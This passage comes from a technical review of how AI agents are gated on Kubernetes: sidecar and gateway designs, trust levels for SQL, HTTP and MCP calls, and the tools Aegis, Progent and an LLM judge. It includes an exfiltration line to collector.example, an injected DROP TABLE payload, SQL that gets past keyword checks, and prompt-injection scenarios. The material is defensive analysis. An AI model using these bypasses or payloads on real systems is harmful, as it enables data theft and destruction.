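The token that the sidecar uses to log in to Vault could defeat credential isolation. According to *Kubernetes service account tokens*, most pods receive this token by default, at the path where Sharif's sidecar reads it. The default applies to every container in the pod. Vault checks which service account the token belongs to, and the agent and sidecar share one, so an agent that can read the token has the same access to Vault as the gate.

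The token must therefore be present in the sidecar only, and nothing in Sharif's specification of the webhook ensures this. The operator can turn off the automatic mount for the whole pod and add the token to the sidecar by hand. The relevant parts of the pod description would look like this:

```yaml
spec:
  automountServiceAccountToken: false
  initContainers:
  - name: agentmesh-sidecar
    restartPolicy: Always
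    volumeMounts:
    - name: vault-token
      mountPath: /var/run/secrets/kubernetes.io/serviceaccount
      readOnly: true
  containers:
  - name: support-agent        # no token here
  volumes:
  - name: vault-token
    projected:
      sources:
      - serviceAccountToken:
          path: token
          audience: vault
          expirationSeconds: 600
```

The `audience` line marks the token as intended for Vault, so the API server won't accept it as a login to the cluster. The operator should also configure Vault to accept only tokens with that audience. Kubernetes' *Configure Service Accounts for Pods* explains that tokens mounted this way expire, unlike the long-term ones that versions before 1.22 created automatically.

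An agent that manages the cluster needs its own Kubernetes token. The token should have a different audience, so that Vault rejects it, and the agent must not have permission to issue new tokens for its account. Podala Narasimha withholds that permission from agents, along with permission to read Secrets or run commands in other containers. The pod must also leave `shareProcessNamespace` off, because turning it on would let the agent see the sidecar's processes and possibly its files.

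### A credential proxy for nine healthcare agents

*Caging the Agents* (Maiti, 2026) describes a simpler design in its account of nine agents in production at a healthcare technology company. A sidecar holds the keys for Anthropic, GitHub and other services. To call a Claude model, the agent sends its request to `localhost:8443/v1/messages`, and the sidecar adds the key and forwards the request to Anthropic. The sidecar also limits the rate, size and destination of requests, but it has no trust levels. Because the agent addresses the sidecar directly, the design doesn't need packet redirection or a certificate authority.

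The sidecar gate needs credential isolation because network policies apply to the whole pod. Maiti restricts each pod to an approved list of hosts, but the agent shares that list with the sidecar and could connect to Anthropic directly. With credential isolation, it would have no key. Maiti also writes that the policies log blocked connections, but standard NetworkPolicy can't do this, so the network plugin would have to.

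The paper's findings show why the company wanted such a sidecar. On 11 March 2026, another AI agent audited the fleet and found four serious problems on three of the nine machines:

- One agent's shell configuration file contained 12 credentials, including a GitHub token.
- On that machine and a second one, every process could read the file that held the agent's stored credentials.
- A third machine's shell configuration exposed a key for Amazon's model service.

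Automated procedures fixed all four problems the same day. The other six machines had no findings above low severity.

These findings provide little evidence about whether the sidecar works, because all nine agents were running on virtual machines. Maiti calls the Kubernetes design the "current migration target", and even the newest machine image kept credentials in local files. The abstract mentions results from a 90-day deployment, but the dated steps run from 3 February to 11 March, which is 36 days. Maiti also says the architecture mitigates nine of eleven problems from an earlier study of agent failures. This claim is based on a written comparison, and Maiti doesn't report trying the attacks against the finished design.

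### A shared gateway in its own pod

Network policies can distinguish between pods, so they can enforce the use of a gate that runs in its own pod. Podala Narasimha's reference architecture works this way. Agents send their tool calls to a shared gateway, which checks each call and passes it to a tool server. The tool servers hold the credentials, and each runs under its own service account. An agent pod may connect only to DNS, the gateway and one model endpoint, and has no network route to the Kubernetes API server.

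According to the Kubernetes documentation, NetworkPolicy can't force traffic through a common gateway. This architecture instead uses it to block the other routes, so if a developer forgets to point an agent at the gateway, the agent's tool calls fail.

Model calls are an exception because Podala Narasimha makes routing them through the gateway optional. The sample policy lets agents connect directly to Amazon's model service with a cloud identity that can do nothing else. When agents connect directly, the gateway can't check which model they use or what data they send, and Podala Narasimha acknowledges that sensitive data can leave this way. An operator who wants to apply rules like Sharif's to models has to block this route and send model calls through the gateway. The sample policy also lets agents look up any name in DNS, which the operator should limit to approved names.

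The architecture's validating policies also apply when someone uses a stolen token to request a cluster change outside the gateway. Podala Narasimha reports no measurements of attacks stopped or of overhead, and the assessment of which layers stop which threats is the author's own. In one proposed experiment, the operator switches off the upper layers and checks whether the layer below still blocks the harmful call. This test would be useful for any of these designs.

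A shared gateway also has to identify its callers. A sidecar serves one pod, so calls over the local interface come from that pod's agent. With Tuskira's gateway, each agent sends a gateway key and the name of a profile, which lists the tools the agent may use. Help Net Security warns that if a key has no profile attached, its holder can ask for any profile. So the operator has to attach a profile to every key.

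### Sidecars, shared gateways and node-level proxies compared

A third option is one proxy per node. Red Hat tested this in January 2026 with Kagenti, which uses a node-level Istio proxy called ztunnel. When a pod in an unauthorised namespace tried to call an agent, ztunnel reset the connection before any HTTP exchange. But ztunnel ignores rules about HTTP methods, which need a waypoint proxy. A node-level proxy like this can control which workloads connect to each other, but it can't apply trust levels to individual calls.

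| | Gate in each pod | Shared gateway | Proxy on each node |
|---|---|---|---|
| Isolation from the agent | Separate container, same network address | Separate pod | Separate pod on the same node |
| Extra network path | Within the pod | To another pod, often on another node | Within the node |
| Memory use grows with | Number of agents | Traffic and number of copies | Number of nodes |
| One failure affects | One agent | All agents, if there is only one copy | All agents on the node |

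Sharif reserves 32 MiB of memory for each sidecar and allows it up to 64 MiB. Sidecars for 100 agents would therefore reserve about 3.1 GiB and use up to 6.3 GiB. Red Hat calls per-pod proxies a waste of memory and processor time for agents that run language models, but gives no figures. The objection matters less for an agent that calls a model hosted elsewhere, because its pod doesn't run the model.

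The limits on each sidecar may cause more trouble than the total. Each sidecar has 64 MiB of memory and a tenth of a processor core to decrypt requests, parse them, compute hashes and sign records. A model request that contains several large images could fill much of that memory. If the sidecar exceeds its memory limit, the kernel kills it, and the agent's calls fail until the sidecar restarts.

How much a gate slows a call depends on the type of call. Maiti puts a model's response time at 500 to 3,000 milliseconds, so a few extra milliseconds at a gate would hardly matter. A simple database query can finish in a millisecond or two, so adding a network hop or creating a new database account could take longer than the query itself. Measurements of ordinary mesh proxies would probably understate the delay of Sharif's gate, which, for example, has to write a signed record to disk before it returns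 a model's response.

### What an attacker gains by taking over the gate

Sharif acknowledges that an attacker who controls a sidecar can admit any call, forge ledger records and use the sidecar's signing key and Vault tokens. Such an attack is plausible because the sidecar has to parse SQL and HTTP requests that an attacker may have influenced through the agent. Sharif runs the sidecar without root access or Linux capabilities and with a read-only filesystem, and recommends signed images and runtime monitoring. These measures make it harder to tamper with the sidecar or move from it to the node, but they don't protect the credentials the sidecar can request.

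If an attacker takes over a sidecar, the damage should be limited to one agent, whereas a shared gateway may hold access for all of them. Sharif's configuration loses much of this advantage because its policy file names one Vault role and one type of database account, and that role accepts every service account that agent pods use. An attacker who took over the sidecar of a read-only agent could therefore get the same database rights as the sidecar of an administrator's agent. To prevent this, the operator has to give each group of agents its own service account and Vault role, with matching database rights. Each group also needs its own namespace, because each namespace has only one policy file.

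In Podala Narasimha's architecture, the gateway decides which tool calls to allow, and the tool servers hold their own credentials. An attacker who controlled the gateway could approve any tool call but wouldn't obtain those credentials. The API server would also still reject cluster changes that its validating policies forbid.

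## How the gate decides what level a call requires

If the gate can read a call, it must then determine which trust level the call requires. Sharif derives this level from the model's name for model calls, the first keyword for SQL statements and the method for HTTP requests. The levels for SQL and HTTP are fixed. Operators set the levels for models, so the last column of this table shows only Sharif's example policy.

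| Required level | SQL keyword | HTTP method | Models in the example policy |
|---|---|---|---|
| L0 | SELECT, SHOW, DESCRIBE, EXPLAIN | GET, HEAD, OPTIONS | `text-embedding-3-small` |
| L1 | INSERT | POST | `gpt-4o-mini`, `gpt-4o`, `claude-sonnet-4-20250514` |
| L2 | UPDATE, CREATE | PUT, PATCH | `gpt-4o-with-tools`, `claude-opus-4-20250514` |
| L3 | ALTER, DELETE | DELETE | `o3-pro`, `medical-diagnosis-v2` |
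| L4 | DROP, TRUNCATE, GRANT, REVOKE | (none) | `autonomous-trading-v1` |

Operators can add rules for particular tables, columns and API routes. A query that refers to a column whose name suggests personal data, such as `email`, requires at least L3. If several levels apply to a call, the gate takes the highest:

```
SQL:   required level = max(keyword level, table level, column level)
HTTP:  required level = max(method level, route level)
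```

With Sharif's sample rules, this gives the following results for three calls:

| Call | Level from its form | Other levels that apply | Required level |
|---|---|---|---|
| `SELECT title FROM public_content` | L0 | Table rule: L0 | L0 |
| `SELECT email FROM users` | L0 | Column rule: L3 | L3 |
| `GET /api/v1/transfers` | L0 | Route rule: L3 | L3 |

An agent at L1 could make only the call to the public table. When a query contains several statements, the gate also uses the highest level that any of them requires, so `SELECT * FROM users; DROP TABLE users;` requires L4.

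Because the gate takes the maximum, an extra rule can raise the required level but never lower it. The sample policy sets L0 for paths one segment below `/api/v1/public/`, such as `/api/v1/public/news`, but a POST to one of them still requires L1. Sharif writes elsewhere in the draft that route rules "override" the method's level, which would let an operator lower it. But the formula and Sharif's examples both use the maximum, so that is the safer reading.

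A single scale also ties unrelated permissions together. Suppose a customer service agent looks up an order by the customer's email address. The query refers to a personal-data column, so it requires L3, although Sharif recommends L1 for such agents. If the operator raises the agent to L3, the agent can also delete rows from any table that has no stricter rule. Sharif's certificates can list separate capabilities such as `db:select`, which would let an operator grant reading without deleting, but the gates don't use that list when they evaluate a call.

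### SQL statements that do more than their first keyword suggests

Sharif rates EXPLAIN as L0 because it normally shows how the database would run a statement without running it. In PostgreSQL, however, EXPLAIN ANALYZE runs the statement and reports how long each step took. An agent at L0 could therefore delete every order with a statement that the gate considers harmless. Other PostgreSQL statements cause similar problems:

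| Statement | Effect | Level by first keyword |
|---|---|---|
| `EXPLAIN ANALYZE DELETE FROM orders` | Deletes every order | L0 |
| `SELECT close_account(42)` | Runs a stored function, which may change data | L0 |
| `INSERT INTO prices VALUES (7, 10) ON CONFLICT (id) DO UPDATE SET price = 10` | Overwrites the price if the row exists | L1 |
| `WITH gone AS (DELETE FROM orders RETURNING *) SELECT * FROM gone` | Deletes every order and returns the deleted rows | Not specified |

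The INSERT breaks Sharif's own rule that an L1 agent must not modify existing records. WITH is missing from Sharif's table, and the draft doesn't give a level for SQL keywords that aren't in the table. If the gate refused every statement that starts with one, it would block many ordinary reports, since analysts often start a long SELECT with WITH. If it used the default level, the deletion above would require only L1.

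A gate could fix most of this by parsing the whole statement and requiring the highest level that any operation in it needs. That would catch every case in the table except the function call, because the function's code is in the database and the gate never receives it.

The database can catch that case if the gate runs every L0 statement in a read-only transaction. PostgreSQL then rejects any attempt to change a permanent table, including attempts inside a function or under EXPLAIN ANALYZE. A function could still do harm outside the database, for example by sending a request to another server, so the operator should also limit which functions the gate's database account may run.

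### Personal data in columns that the query does not name

The gate recognises personal data by column name. Sharif's list includes `phone`, `ssn`, `last_name`, `city`, `date_of_birth`, `credit_card` and `ip_address`, and operators can extend it. The draft recommends this check but does not require it.

`SELECT email FROM users` requires L3, but `SELECT * FROM users` returns the same addresses along with every other column and requires only L0. The asterisk names no column, and Sharif doesn't give the gate the database's structure, which it could use to expand the asterisk. Rules for individual columns have the same gap. The sample policy requires L4 for `users.ssn`, but an L0 agent could get the social security numbers with `SELECT * FROM users`.

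Name matching also misses personal data in columns with unremarkable names, such as a `message` column that contains customers' letters. It is too strict in other cases. A list of warehouses may have a `city` column, and web server logs usually record `ip_address` and `user_agent`, which are both on Sharif's list. Sharif considers L0 appropriate for agents that analyse logs, but at that level the gate would refuse queries that name these columns.

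A rule for the whole table is more reliable. If the operator requires L3 for `users`, an agent can't avoid the requirement by writing `SELECT *`. Agents at lower levels can query a view (a saved query that behaves like a table) that leaves out the personal columns. The operator can also restrict columns in the database itself. PostgreSQL rejects `SELECT *` if the account lacks permission to read even one of the table's columns.

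### Model names and HTTP methods

For a model call, the gate reads the model's name from the request's `model` field. The example policy requires L1 for `gpt-4o` and L2 for `gpt-4o-with-tools` because Sharif considers function calling, in which a model proposes tool calls in a structured format, more sensitive. But clients send `gpt-4o` whether or not they use tools, and list any tools in a separate field. The L2 entry therefore never matches, so an L1 agent can use GPT-4o with any tools.

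The gate could check the field that lists the tools, but then an L1 agent would lose function calling, which most agents need in order to act. Sharif's customer service agent at L1 could write replies but could hardly look up an order. Fixing the check would therefore also require revising the levels.

Matching model names exactly causes another problem, because providers often offer the same model under both a short name and a longer, dated one. A rule for `o3-pro` doesn't cover the dated name, so a call that uses it gets the default level, L1, instead of L3.

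The HTTP table rates GET as L0 because a GET request should not change anything on the server. But the request itself can carry data out. An agent that follows an injected instruction could put a customer list in a web address:

```
GET https://collector.example/p?d=<encoded customer list>
```

Whoever runs that server can read the list in its logs. Sharif's route rules specify a path but no host, so the gate requires L0 whether the request goes to the company's own API or to an attacker. The network policies have to stop this call with their list of approved destinations.

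Route rules can also miss longer paths. In Sharif's patterns, `*` matches one path segment and `**` matches any number. The sample rule for `/api/v1/transfers` contains neither, so it doesn't cover `/api/v1/transfers/1042/approve`. A POST that approves a transfer would require only L1 until the operator adds a rule ending in `/**`.

Sharif also has an optional check on access tokens. It compares the agent's level with every permission in the token, so a harmless read with an administrator's token requires L3. This encourages operators to issue narrow tokens, but the check works only if the token lists its permissions in a form the gate can read, and many tokens are random strings.

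Some APIs use POST for every operation. In Amazon's DynamoDB database, for example, reading an item and deleting a whole table are both POST requests to the same path, and a header names the operation. Sharif's gate requires L1 for both.

### Tool calls over MCP

MCP has the same problem, and it affects far more agents. According to Model Context Protocol's *Streamable HTTP*, the client sends each message as a separate POST request to a single address on the server. The previous version of the specification (Model Context Protocol, 2025) also required POST for every message. Without a route rule, Sharif's gate therefore requires L1 both for a tool that reads an order and for one that deletes it.

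A route rule for a server's address raises the level required for every tool on that server. No rule can lower it below L1, so an L0 agent can't use even a read-only tool or list the server's tools. An operator can keep the other tools at a lower level by putting the dangerous ones on a second server with its own address and a stricter route rule.

To rate each tool separately, the gate has to know which tool the agent is calling. This became easier on 28 July 2026, a month before Sharif's draft, when a new version of MCP added the tool's name to the HTTP headers. A shortened request to delete an order now looks like this:

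```http
POST /mcp HTTP/1.1
Mcp-Name: delete_order
Mcp-Method: tools/call
MCP-Protocol-Version: 2026-07-28

{"jsonrpc": "2.0", "id": 7, "method": "tools/call",
 "params": {"name": "delete_order",
            "arguments": {"order_id": 1042}}}
```

Gateways can now authorise calls directly from the request headers, according to the release announcement (Model Context Protocol, 2026). Model Context Protocol's *HTTP standardization* explains that a proxy previously had to decrypt the request and parse the whole body to find the tool's name. The gate still has to decrypt the request to read the headers.

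A gate can't safely decide from the headers alone, because the agent's side writes both the header and the body. A compromised agent could put `get_order` in the header and `delete_order` in the body. Servers that follow the new version must compare the two and reject a mismatch, but a server built for an older version may run the tool named in the body. The Model Context Protocol therefore recommends that gateways reject requests whose version header is missing or too old. A gate can also avoid relying on the server for this check by parsing the body and making the comparison itself.

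The gate also has to decode names, because a client may send them in Base64, a way of writing any text with a limited set of characters. For example, `delete_order` becomes `=?base64?ZGVsZXRlX29yZGVy?=`. The server decodes this before it compares the header with the body. If the gate did not decode it too, its rule for `delete_order` would not match.

Even the correct name may not reveal what the call does. The specification includes an example tool, `execute_sql`, that takes a region and a query. The server's developer can mark simple arguments for copying into headers, and the example marks the region. The query appears only in the body, so a SELECT and a DROP have identical headers. The gate has to read the query from the body and classify it as the database gate would.

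Sharif's draft would need several additions to handle MCP properly:

- The trust policy needs a level for each tool on each server, and this level has to replace the one for POST so that read-only tools can be L0.
- The gate has to parse the message body and check that it matches the headers.
- For tools that accept SQL or other code, the gate has to classify the relevant argument.
- A tool that the policy doesn't list should be off limits until someone rates it.

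None of this helps when the MCP server runs inside the agent's container. The agent and the server can then exchange messages directly, without HTTP, and the gate can check only the server's outbound connections.

### Scanning arguments for signs of attack

Some systems examine what the arguments contain instead of assigning a level to the operation. Yuan, Su and Zhao (2026), in *AEGIS*, describe a tool that works this way. In their example, a user asks an agent to summarise customer feedback, and an instruction hidden in the feedback makes the model propose this call:

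```
execute_sql("SELECT * FROM users; DROP TABLE audit_log; --")
```

Sharif's database gate would require L4 for this query if it arrived over a database connection. Over MCP, the same query would arrive in a POST request and require L1.

Aegis changes the software library that the agent uses to call its model. When the model's reply proposes a tool call, the library pauses the agent and sends the tool's name and arguments to a separate service, which checks them in three stages:

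1. It extracts every piece of text from the arguments, down to 32 levels of nesting and up to 10,000 pieces. If an argument exceeds these limits, the service treats the call as suspicious.
2. It compares the text with 22 patterns. Seven cover SQL injection, and the others cover shell commands, file paths that escape their folder, prompt injection, sensitive files, data theft and personal data.
3. It checks the call against the operator's policies, which specify the form that arguments may take.

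The service then allows the call, blocks it or holds it for a person to review. Because Aegis acts on the model's reply, it can also stop commands that run inside the agent's own container, which a gate on outbound calls can't detect. But it doesn't cover calls that the agent makes without the modified library, so an agent that can write and run its own code may be able to bypass it.

Yuan and colleagues tested Aegis on 48 attacks, and it stopped all of them. The set included 11 SQL injections, 11 prompt injections and eight shell injections, but only two attempts to steal data. Aegis also wrongly stopped six of 500 harmless calls. In a test of 1,000 calls on a local installation, it added a median delay of 8.3 milliseconds, and the delay was no more than about 23 milliseconds for 99 percent of calls.

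The perfect score is weak evidence of how Aegis would perform against a real attacker. Yuan and colleagues chose the 48 attacks from known techniques, and the patterns target the same techniques. An attacker can rewrite an attack until no pattern matches, and public access to the code makes this easier. Yuan and colleagues acknowledge that Aegis may miss new variants.

Even if the 48 attacks were a random sample of all attacks, the 95 percent upper bound on Aegis's miss rate would be about 6 percent, which is fairly high. If Aegis misses a share *p* of attacks, the chance that it stops 48 in a row is (1 − *p*)^48, which falls to 5 percent when *p* is about 0.06.

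The false alarms matter more in daily use. Six out of 500 is 1.2 percent, so an operator whose agents make 10,000 harmless calls a day could expect the gate to wrongly stop about 120 of them. The sample is small, and the true rate could plausibly be between 0.4 and 2.6 percent, or roughly 40 to 260 stops a day. If one call in 10,000 were a real attack, a reviewer would see about 120 false alarms for each genuine one.

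The errors also depend heavily on the type of work. All six false alarms came from ordinary SQL queries with OR in their conditions, which resemble a common form of SQL injection. An agent that writes database reports would trigger many more false alarms than one that sends emails. Yuan and colleagues suggest exceptions for particular tools, but in their design the content of the arguments overrides these exceptions, so it isn't clear that they would work.

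Another, more basic limit of pattern matching is that a harmful call may contain no suspicious text. For example, an injected instruction could prompt the call `delete_order(order_id=1042)`. Aegis would need a specific policy to stop this call, whereas a gate that assigns each tool a required level would block it for any agent below L3.

### Rules about arguments

Operators can also write rules about which arguments a tool may receive. In *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025), each rule names a tool and sets conditions on its arguments, such as a fixed value or a text pattern. Progent blocks any call that no rule allows, and the same call under the same rules always gets the same result.

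Unlike Sharif's levels, the rules depend on the user's task. Sending an email is right if the user asked the agent to email Alice, but it may be data theft if the user asked only for a summary of the inbox. A language model therefore writes the initial rules from the user's request and proposes changes as the agent learns more.

In one example, the user asks an agent to carry out the tasks in an email from Alice. At first, the rules allow only a search for that email. In it, Alice asks for a Slack message summarizing recent emails, so the model proposes rules that allow the agent to read emails and send Slack messages. When the agent finds the Slack username `alice`, the model narrows the Slack rule to messages for `alice`. One of the recent emails contains an injected instruction to forward the inbox to `eve@evil.com`. No rule allows sending email, so Progent blocks the call, and the agent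 then posts the summary.

The injected text could also fool the model that writes the rules. Progent therefore checks each proposed change with an SMT solver, a program that can prove whether one set of logical conditions contains another. Progent applies the change automatically if the new rules allow nothing that the old ones blocked; otherwise, someone has to approve it first.

Shi and colleagues tested Progent on two collections of simulated attacks on agents. The share of successful attacks fell from 39.9 to 1.0 percent on AgentDojo and from 70.3 to 3.9 percent on ASB. The agents still completed their legitimate tasks about as well as before. On AgentDojo, only 6 percent of rule changes needed approval. These results are more informative than the Aegis test because the attacks come from established benchmarks and there is a baseline without the defence. However, the sets of attacks were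 fixed, and the results don't show how often a person would wrongly approve a change in practice.

*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) criticises Progent for depending on rules being correct and complete, since people often make mistakes when writing them by hand. It also objects that Progent doesn't cover attacks on the agent's written answers, and that hostile text in a tool's result may lead to looser rules. The approval step addresses the last objection only if the approver is careful, and Progent has a setting that removes this protection by approving every change automatically.

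Approval is harder than the example suggests, because legitimate and malicious changes can arrive in the same way. The request to post on Slack also came from an email. If an attacker had taken over Alice's account, the approver would have had little reason to refuse.

An operator could add rules about a call's arguments to Sharif's gate and write them by hand instead of letting a model write them. For example, the trust policy could require L1 for refunds of up to $50 and L3 for larger ones. This would keep the gate's decisions predictable and address a weakness of the draft, which gives a $5 refund and a $50,000 refund the same level if both use the same route. But the operator would have to write and maintain rules for every important tool, and those rules still wouldn't depend on what the user asked for.

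### A language model as the judge

Google Cloud's *Semantic governance overview* describes a service, currently in preview, that uses a second language model to check each tool call an agent's model proposes. Administrators write the rules in plain English, such as a ban on automatic refunds above $75. A gateway intercepts the agent model's reply and sends the proposed call, the rules and the conversation to the second model, which checks whether the call follows the rules and fits what the user asked for. If either check fails, the gateway replaces the call with an explanation of the refusal.

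This approach can handle distinctions that are difficult to express as levels or patterns. Help Net Security's *Google's semantic governance policies can block an AI agent's tool call* describes a finance team's agent that can search files, send email and delete drafts. A rule restricts unreleased quarterly results to company addresses, so the judge allows an email to the company's controller and blocks one to an outside investor. In Sharif's scheme, both emails would be POST requests to the same route and require the same level. When hidden text in a planning document instructs the agent to delete drafts, the judge blocks the deletion because the user never asked for it.

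However, the judge may give different answers to the same question. Deepti Sehrawat, a software engineer at Google, warns that verdicts "may vary" and recommends a trial run in which the service records its verdicts without enforcing them. Neither Google Cloud's overview nor Help Net Security's report gives an error rate. The judge also reads the conversation, which can include the attacker's text, so an attacker could use an injection to target the judge as well as the agent.

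The judge can use only the information it receives, so if a rule depends on the date of an earnings release, the administrator has to put that date in the agent's instructions. The service doesn't check streamed replies, which arrive a few words at a time, so Google Cloud's *Configure semantic governance policies* requires agents to call their models without streaming. Its sample configuration sends traffic to the judge only if the web address contains one of four known paths for model calls. An agent that called a model at any other address would avoid the check unless another control blocked the connection.

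Google Cloud presents the judge as an addition to ordinary access controls. An operator could combine it with Sharif's gate in the same way, so that a call needs both a sufficient trust level and the judge's approval. A mistaken approval from the judge would then never admit a call that the fixed rules refuse. However, the combination would wrongly refuse more calls, because an error in either check is enough to block a legitimate one. To limit delay and expense, the operator could send only the riskier calls to the judge, but this works only if the gate rates those calls correctly.

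## How an agent gets its trust level and when a person must approve

The gate compares the trust level a call requires with the level the agent has. Sharif defines an agent's level by what the agent may do, and each level includes the rights of the levels below it.

| Level | Name | What the level adds | Typical agents |
|---|---|---|---|
| L0 | Read-only | Reading data | Monitoring, log analysis |
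| L1 | General purpose | Creating new records, using general-purpose models | Customer service, content writing |
| L2 | Specialist | Changing existing records, using models that call tools, delegating to other agents | Data processing, coding, research |
| L3 | Compliance-logged | Deleting records, working in finance, medicine or law | A trading agent |
| L4 | Critical | Destructive or irreversible operations, each with a person's approval | An infrastructure agent |

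L3 also requires the sidecar to record a hash of every request and response, and the operator to keep these records for at least five years for financial work, seven for medical work and ten for nuclear work.

Sharif's definitions reserve delegation for L2 and above, but the gates don't enforce this because none has a rule for detecting delegation. An agent would usually delegate by sending another agent an HTTP POST, which requires only L1. If an L1 agent asks an L3 agent to delete an order, the L3 agent's gate checks only the L3 agent's level and admits the deletion. The draft mentions "delegation trust requirements" but doesn't define them.

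Podala Narasimha addresses a similar problem, in which a user asks an agent for something the user isn't allowed to do. The gateway exchanges the user's token for a narrower one that identifies both the user and the agent, and the tools allow only what both may do. An operator could apply the same rule when one agent asks another to act.

### How the gate finds an agent's level

Sharif lists six places where an agent's level may be set. The gate checks them in this order and uses the first level it finds:

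1. an extension in the agent's certificate
2. the pod annotation `agentmesh.io/trust-level`
3. an entry in the trust policy that matches the agent's identity exactly
4. the longest matching prefix in the trust policy
5. the default for the agent's namespace
6. the global default

If none of them gives a level, the agent gets L1.

Suppose an agent has the SPIFFE identity `spiffe://example.com/agent/trading/bot-1`, and the trust policy has three wildcard entries, taken from an example in the draft:

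| Identities that begin with | Level |
|---|---|
| `spiffe://example.com/` | L0 |
| `spiffe://example.com/agent/` | L1 |
| `spiffe://example.com/agent/trading/` | L3 |

No entry matches exactly, but all three wildcards match. The longest prefix wins, so the agent gets L3, and the gate never looks at the defaults. Other settings can change this result without any edit to the policy:

| Settings | Agent's level |
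|---|---|
| The policy above | L3 |
| The policy and a pod annotation of 4 | L4 |
| The policy, the annotation and a certificate with level 1 | L1 |

A small mismatch in an agent's identity can also change its trust level. Sharif's format for agent identities produces names like `spiffe://example.com/agentmesh/production/trading-bot-1`, but the wildcard in the sample policy matches only names that begin with `spiffe://example.com/agent/`. The agent doesn't match the entry that would have given it L1, so it gets the sample default for the production namespace, which is L2.

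### Who can raise an agent's level

The annotation is the most serious weakness in this order. Whoever deploys a pod writes its annotations, so a developer can give an agent L4 even if the central policy sets L1. An agent that can create pods could do the same for a new pod. Sharif requires operators to restrict who can edit the policy file and forbids the agent's own service account from editing it, but sets no such rule for the annotation.

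Kubernetes' ordinary permissions can't close this gap, because they control who may create pods and not what the pods contain. A validating admission policy can. The simplest one rejects every pod that has the annotation:

```
!has(object.metadata.annotations) ||
!("agentmesh.io/trust-level" in object.metadata.annotations)
```

With this test in place, levels come from the trust policy unless a certificate contains a level. If some teams need the annotation, a better rule would let it lower an agent's level but never raise it. The gate would then have to take the lower of the two levels instead of the first one it finds, as it does now.

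Podala Narasimha warns about a similar mistake with cloud permissions. Annotations on a service account can determine which cloud role an agent gets, so the platform team should control that mapping. Otherwise, an agent that can edit its own namespace could give itself more access.

In Sharif's design, the sidecar requests the agent's certificate and includes the trust level in the request. The draft doesn't specify what the certificate authority should check that level against. If the authority signs whatever it receives, its certificates add no assurance, even though they take precedence over every other setting.

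A certificate can also keep an agent at an old trust level. Certificates last between one and 24 hours, and the sidecar renews them with the same extensions. If an operator lowers an agent from L3 to L1 in the trust policy but the agent's certificate contains L3, the agent stays at L3 even after renewal. The operator then has to change what the authority issues or revoke the agent altogether. Leaving levels out of certificates is simpler, because the gates accept ordinary SPIFFE certificates, which prove only the agent's identity, and can look up the level in the policy.

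### One ordered scale or a list of permissions

A bookkeeping agent raised to L3 for a single financial API also gains every other right up to L3, like the customer service agent that needed L3 to look up an order by email address. Only network access, the credentials that the sidecar can fetch, and any stricter rules for particular tables or routes limit what the bookkeeping agent can reach.

More levels wouldn't solve the problem, because on any ordered scale an agent can do everything that agents at or below its level can do. Suppose a payroll agent needs the payment API, a clinic's agent needs patient records, and both operations require L3. Each agent then passes the gate for the other's work as well. No choice of levels for the agents and operations can give each agent only the access it needs.

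An operator can work around this with separate namespaces, each with its own policy file. The clinic's file could require L4 for payments, and the payroll file could require L4 for patient records. But the operator would then be using levels to write a separate permission list for each group of agents.

Listing what each agent may do is more direct. Podala Narasimha's sample policy gives each agent a set of namespaces and code repositories. An agent may read logs only in its own namespaces and propose changes only to its own repositories, so access to one repository reveals nothing about another. The policy also checks the arguments of each call.

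Lists take more work than levels. With 40 agents and 60 tools, a full set of lists requires 2,400 decisions, while levels require 100 settings, one for each agent and one for each tool. Groups and wildcards shorten the lists, but each wildcard may allow a tool that nobody considered.

Levels are also easier to audit. An auditor can find out which agents may delete records by looking for those at L3 or above instead of comparing 40 lists. This works only if the policy file alone sets the levels. If certificates and annotations can override it, the auditor has to inspect every running pod.

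The third advantage is that the levels give security teams, developers and managers a common vocabulary, provided they all mean the same thing by "L2". Sharif weakens this advantage by matching the levels to those in IEC 62443, a set of security standards for industrial control systems. The IEC 62443 levels describe how capable an attacker a system can withstand, while Sharif's describe how much an agent may do. Raising an agent from L2 to L3 gives it more power without making the system harder to attack, so the claim that an L2 agent meets the standard's requirements for security level 2 doesn't follow.

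An operator can combine both methods by admitting a call only if the agent's level is high enough and its list includes the operation. The level sets a broad limit that is easy to audit, and the list excludes operations the agent doesn't need. Sharif's certificates already have a field for such a list, so the gates would only have to check it.

The resource list also needs a safe default. Microsoft's *AgentMesh Identity and Trust* (2026), a draft specification for the company's open-source Agent Governance Toolkit, combines a trust score with lists of capabilities and resources. (This AgentMesh shares its name with CyberSecAI's product.) But if a credential's resource list is empty, the specification requires the software to allow access to every resource, so an operator who forgets to fill in the list leaves access unrestricted by resource.

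### Levels that an agent earns

In Sharif's enforcement draft, each agent keeps its assigned level until someone changes it. *ATTP* (Sharif, 2026), an earlier draft about trust between agents and services, describes levels that agents earn. A central service gives each agent a score from 0 to 100, based equally on five measures: whether its code matches its declared specification, how often its actions succeed, how consistent its behaviour is, how long it has operated and how few anomalies it has had. The service then adds points for successes and subtracts points for problems.

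| Level in ATTP | Score | Payment limit | Minimum record before promotion to the next level |
|---|---|---|---|
| L0 | 0–19 | None allowed | 24 hours, 5 successful actions |
| L1 | 20–39 | $10 | 7 days, 20 successful actions |
| L2 | 40–59 | $100 | 30 days, 100 successful actions, no critical anomalies |
| L3 | 60–79 | $1,000 | 90 days, 500 successful actions, no anomalies, approval by the agent's owner |
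| L4 | 80–100 | $50,000 | (highest level) |

An agent therefore needs at least 128 days to reach L4, but one critical anomaly sends an L4 agent straight back to L2.

These labels don't mean the same as those in the enforcement draft. An L0 agent has no access in ATTP but can read data under the enforcement draft. At L4, ATTP lets an agent pay $50,000 at a time with extra auditing, while the enforcement draft requires a person to approve each operation. An operator who passed ATTP levels directly to the gates would give new agents access that ATTP denies them.

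The minimum times are meant to prevent trust farming, where an attacker builds a good record with harmless actions and then misuses the access. They slow an attacker down, but the score is easy to inflate. Each success adds half a point, and Sharif sets no separate limit on these points. After 160 successes, an agent has gained 80 points, enough for an L4 score even if all five measures are zero. An agent that completes the minimum of 625 actions has gained more than 300 points on a 100-point scale. If software applied the formula literally, that agent could have more than 40 ordinary anomalies, at five points each, before its score fell below 80.

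Microsoft's toolkit uses a scale from 0 to 1,000, but its documents are inconsistent about how the score works. In the specification, a new agent starts at 500, the score at which actions are "generally permitted". *Agent Governance Toolkit* (mosiddi, 2026), a post on Microsoft's open-source blog, places new agents in the most restricted group, which has scores below 400 and read-only access. Microsoft's *Trust Score Calibration Guide* bases the starting score on where the agent came from, and the toolkit's Rust package, *agentmesh*, has its own defaults.

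| Document | Starting score | Gain | Loss over time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Specification | 500 | 5 points per positive signal | 2 points per hour without a positive signal |
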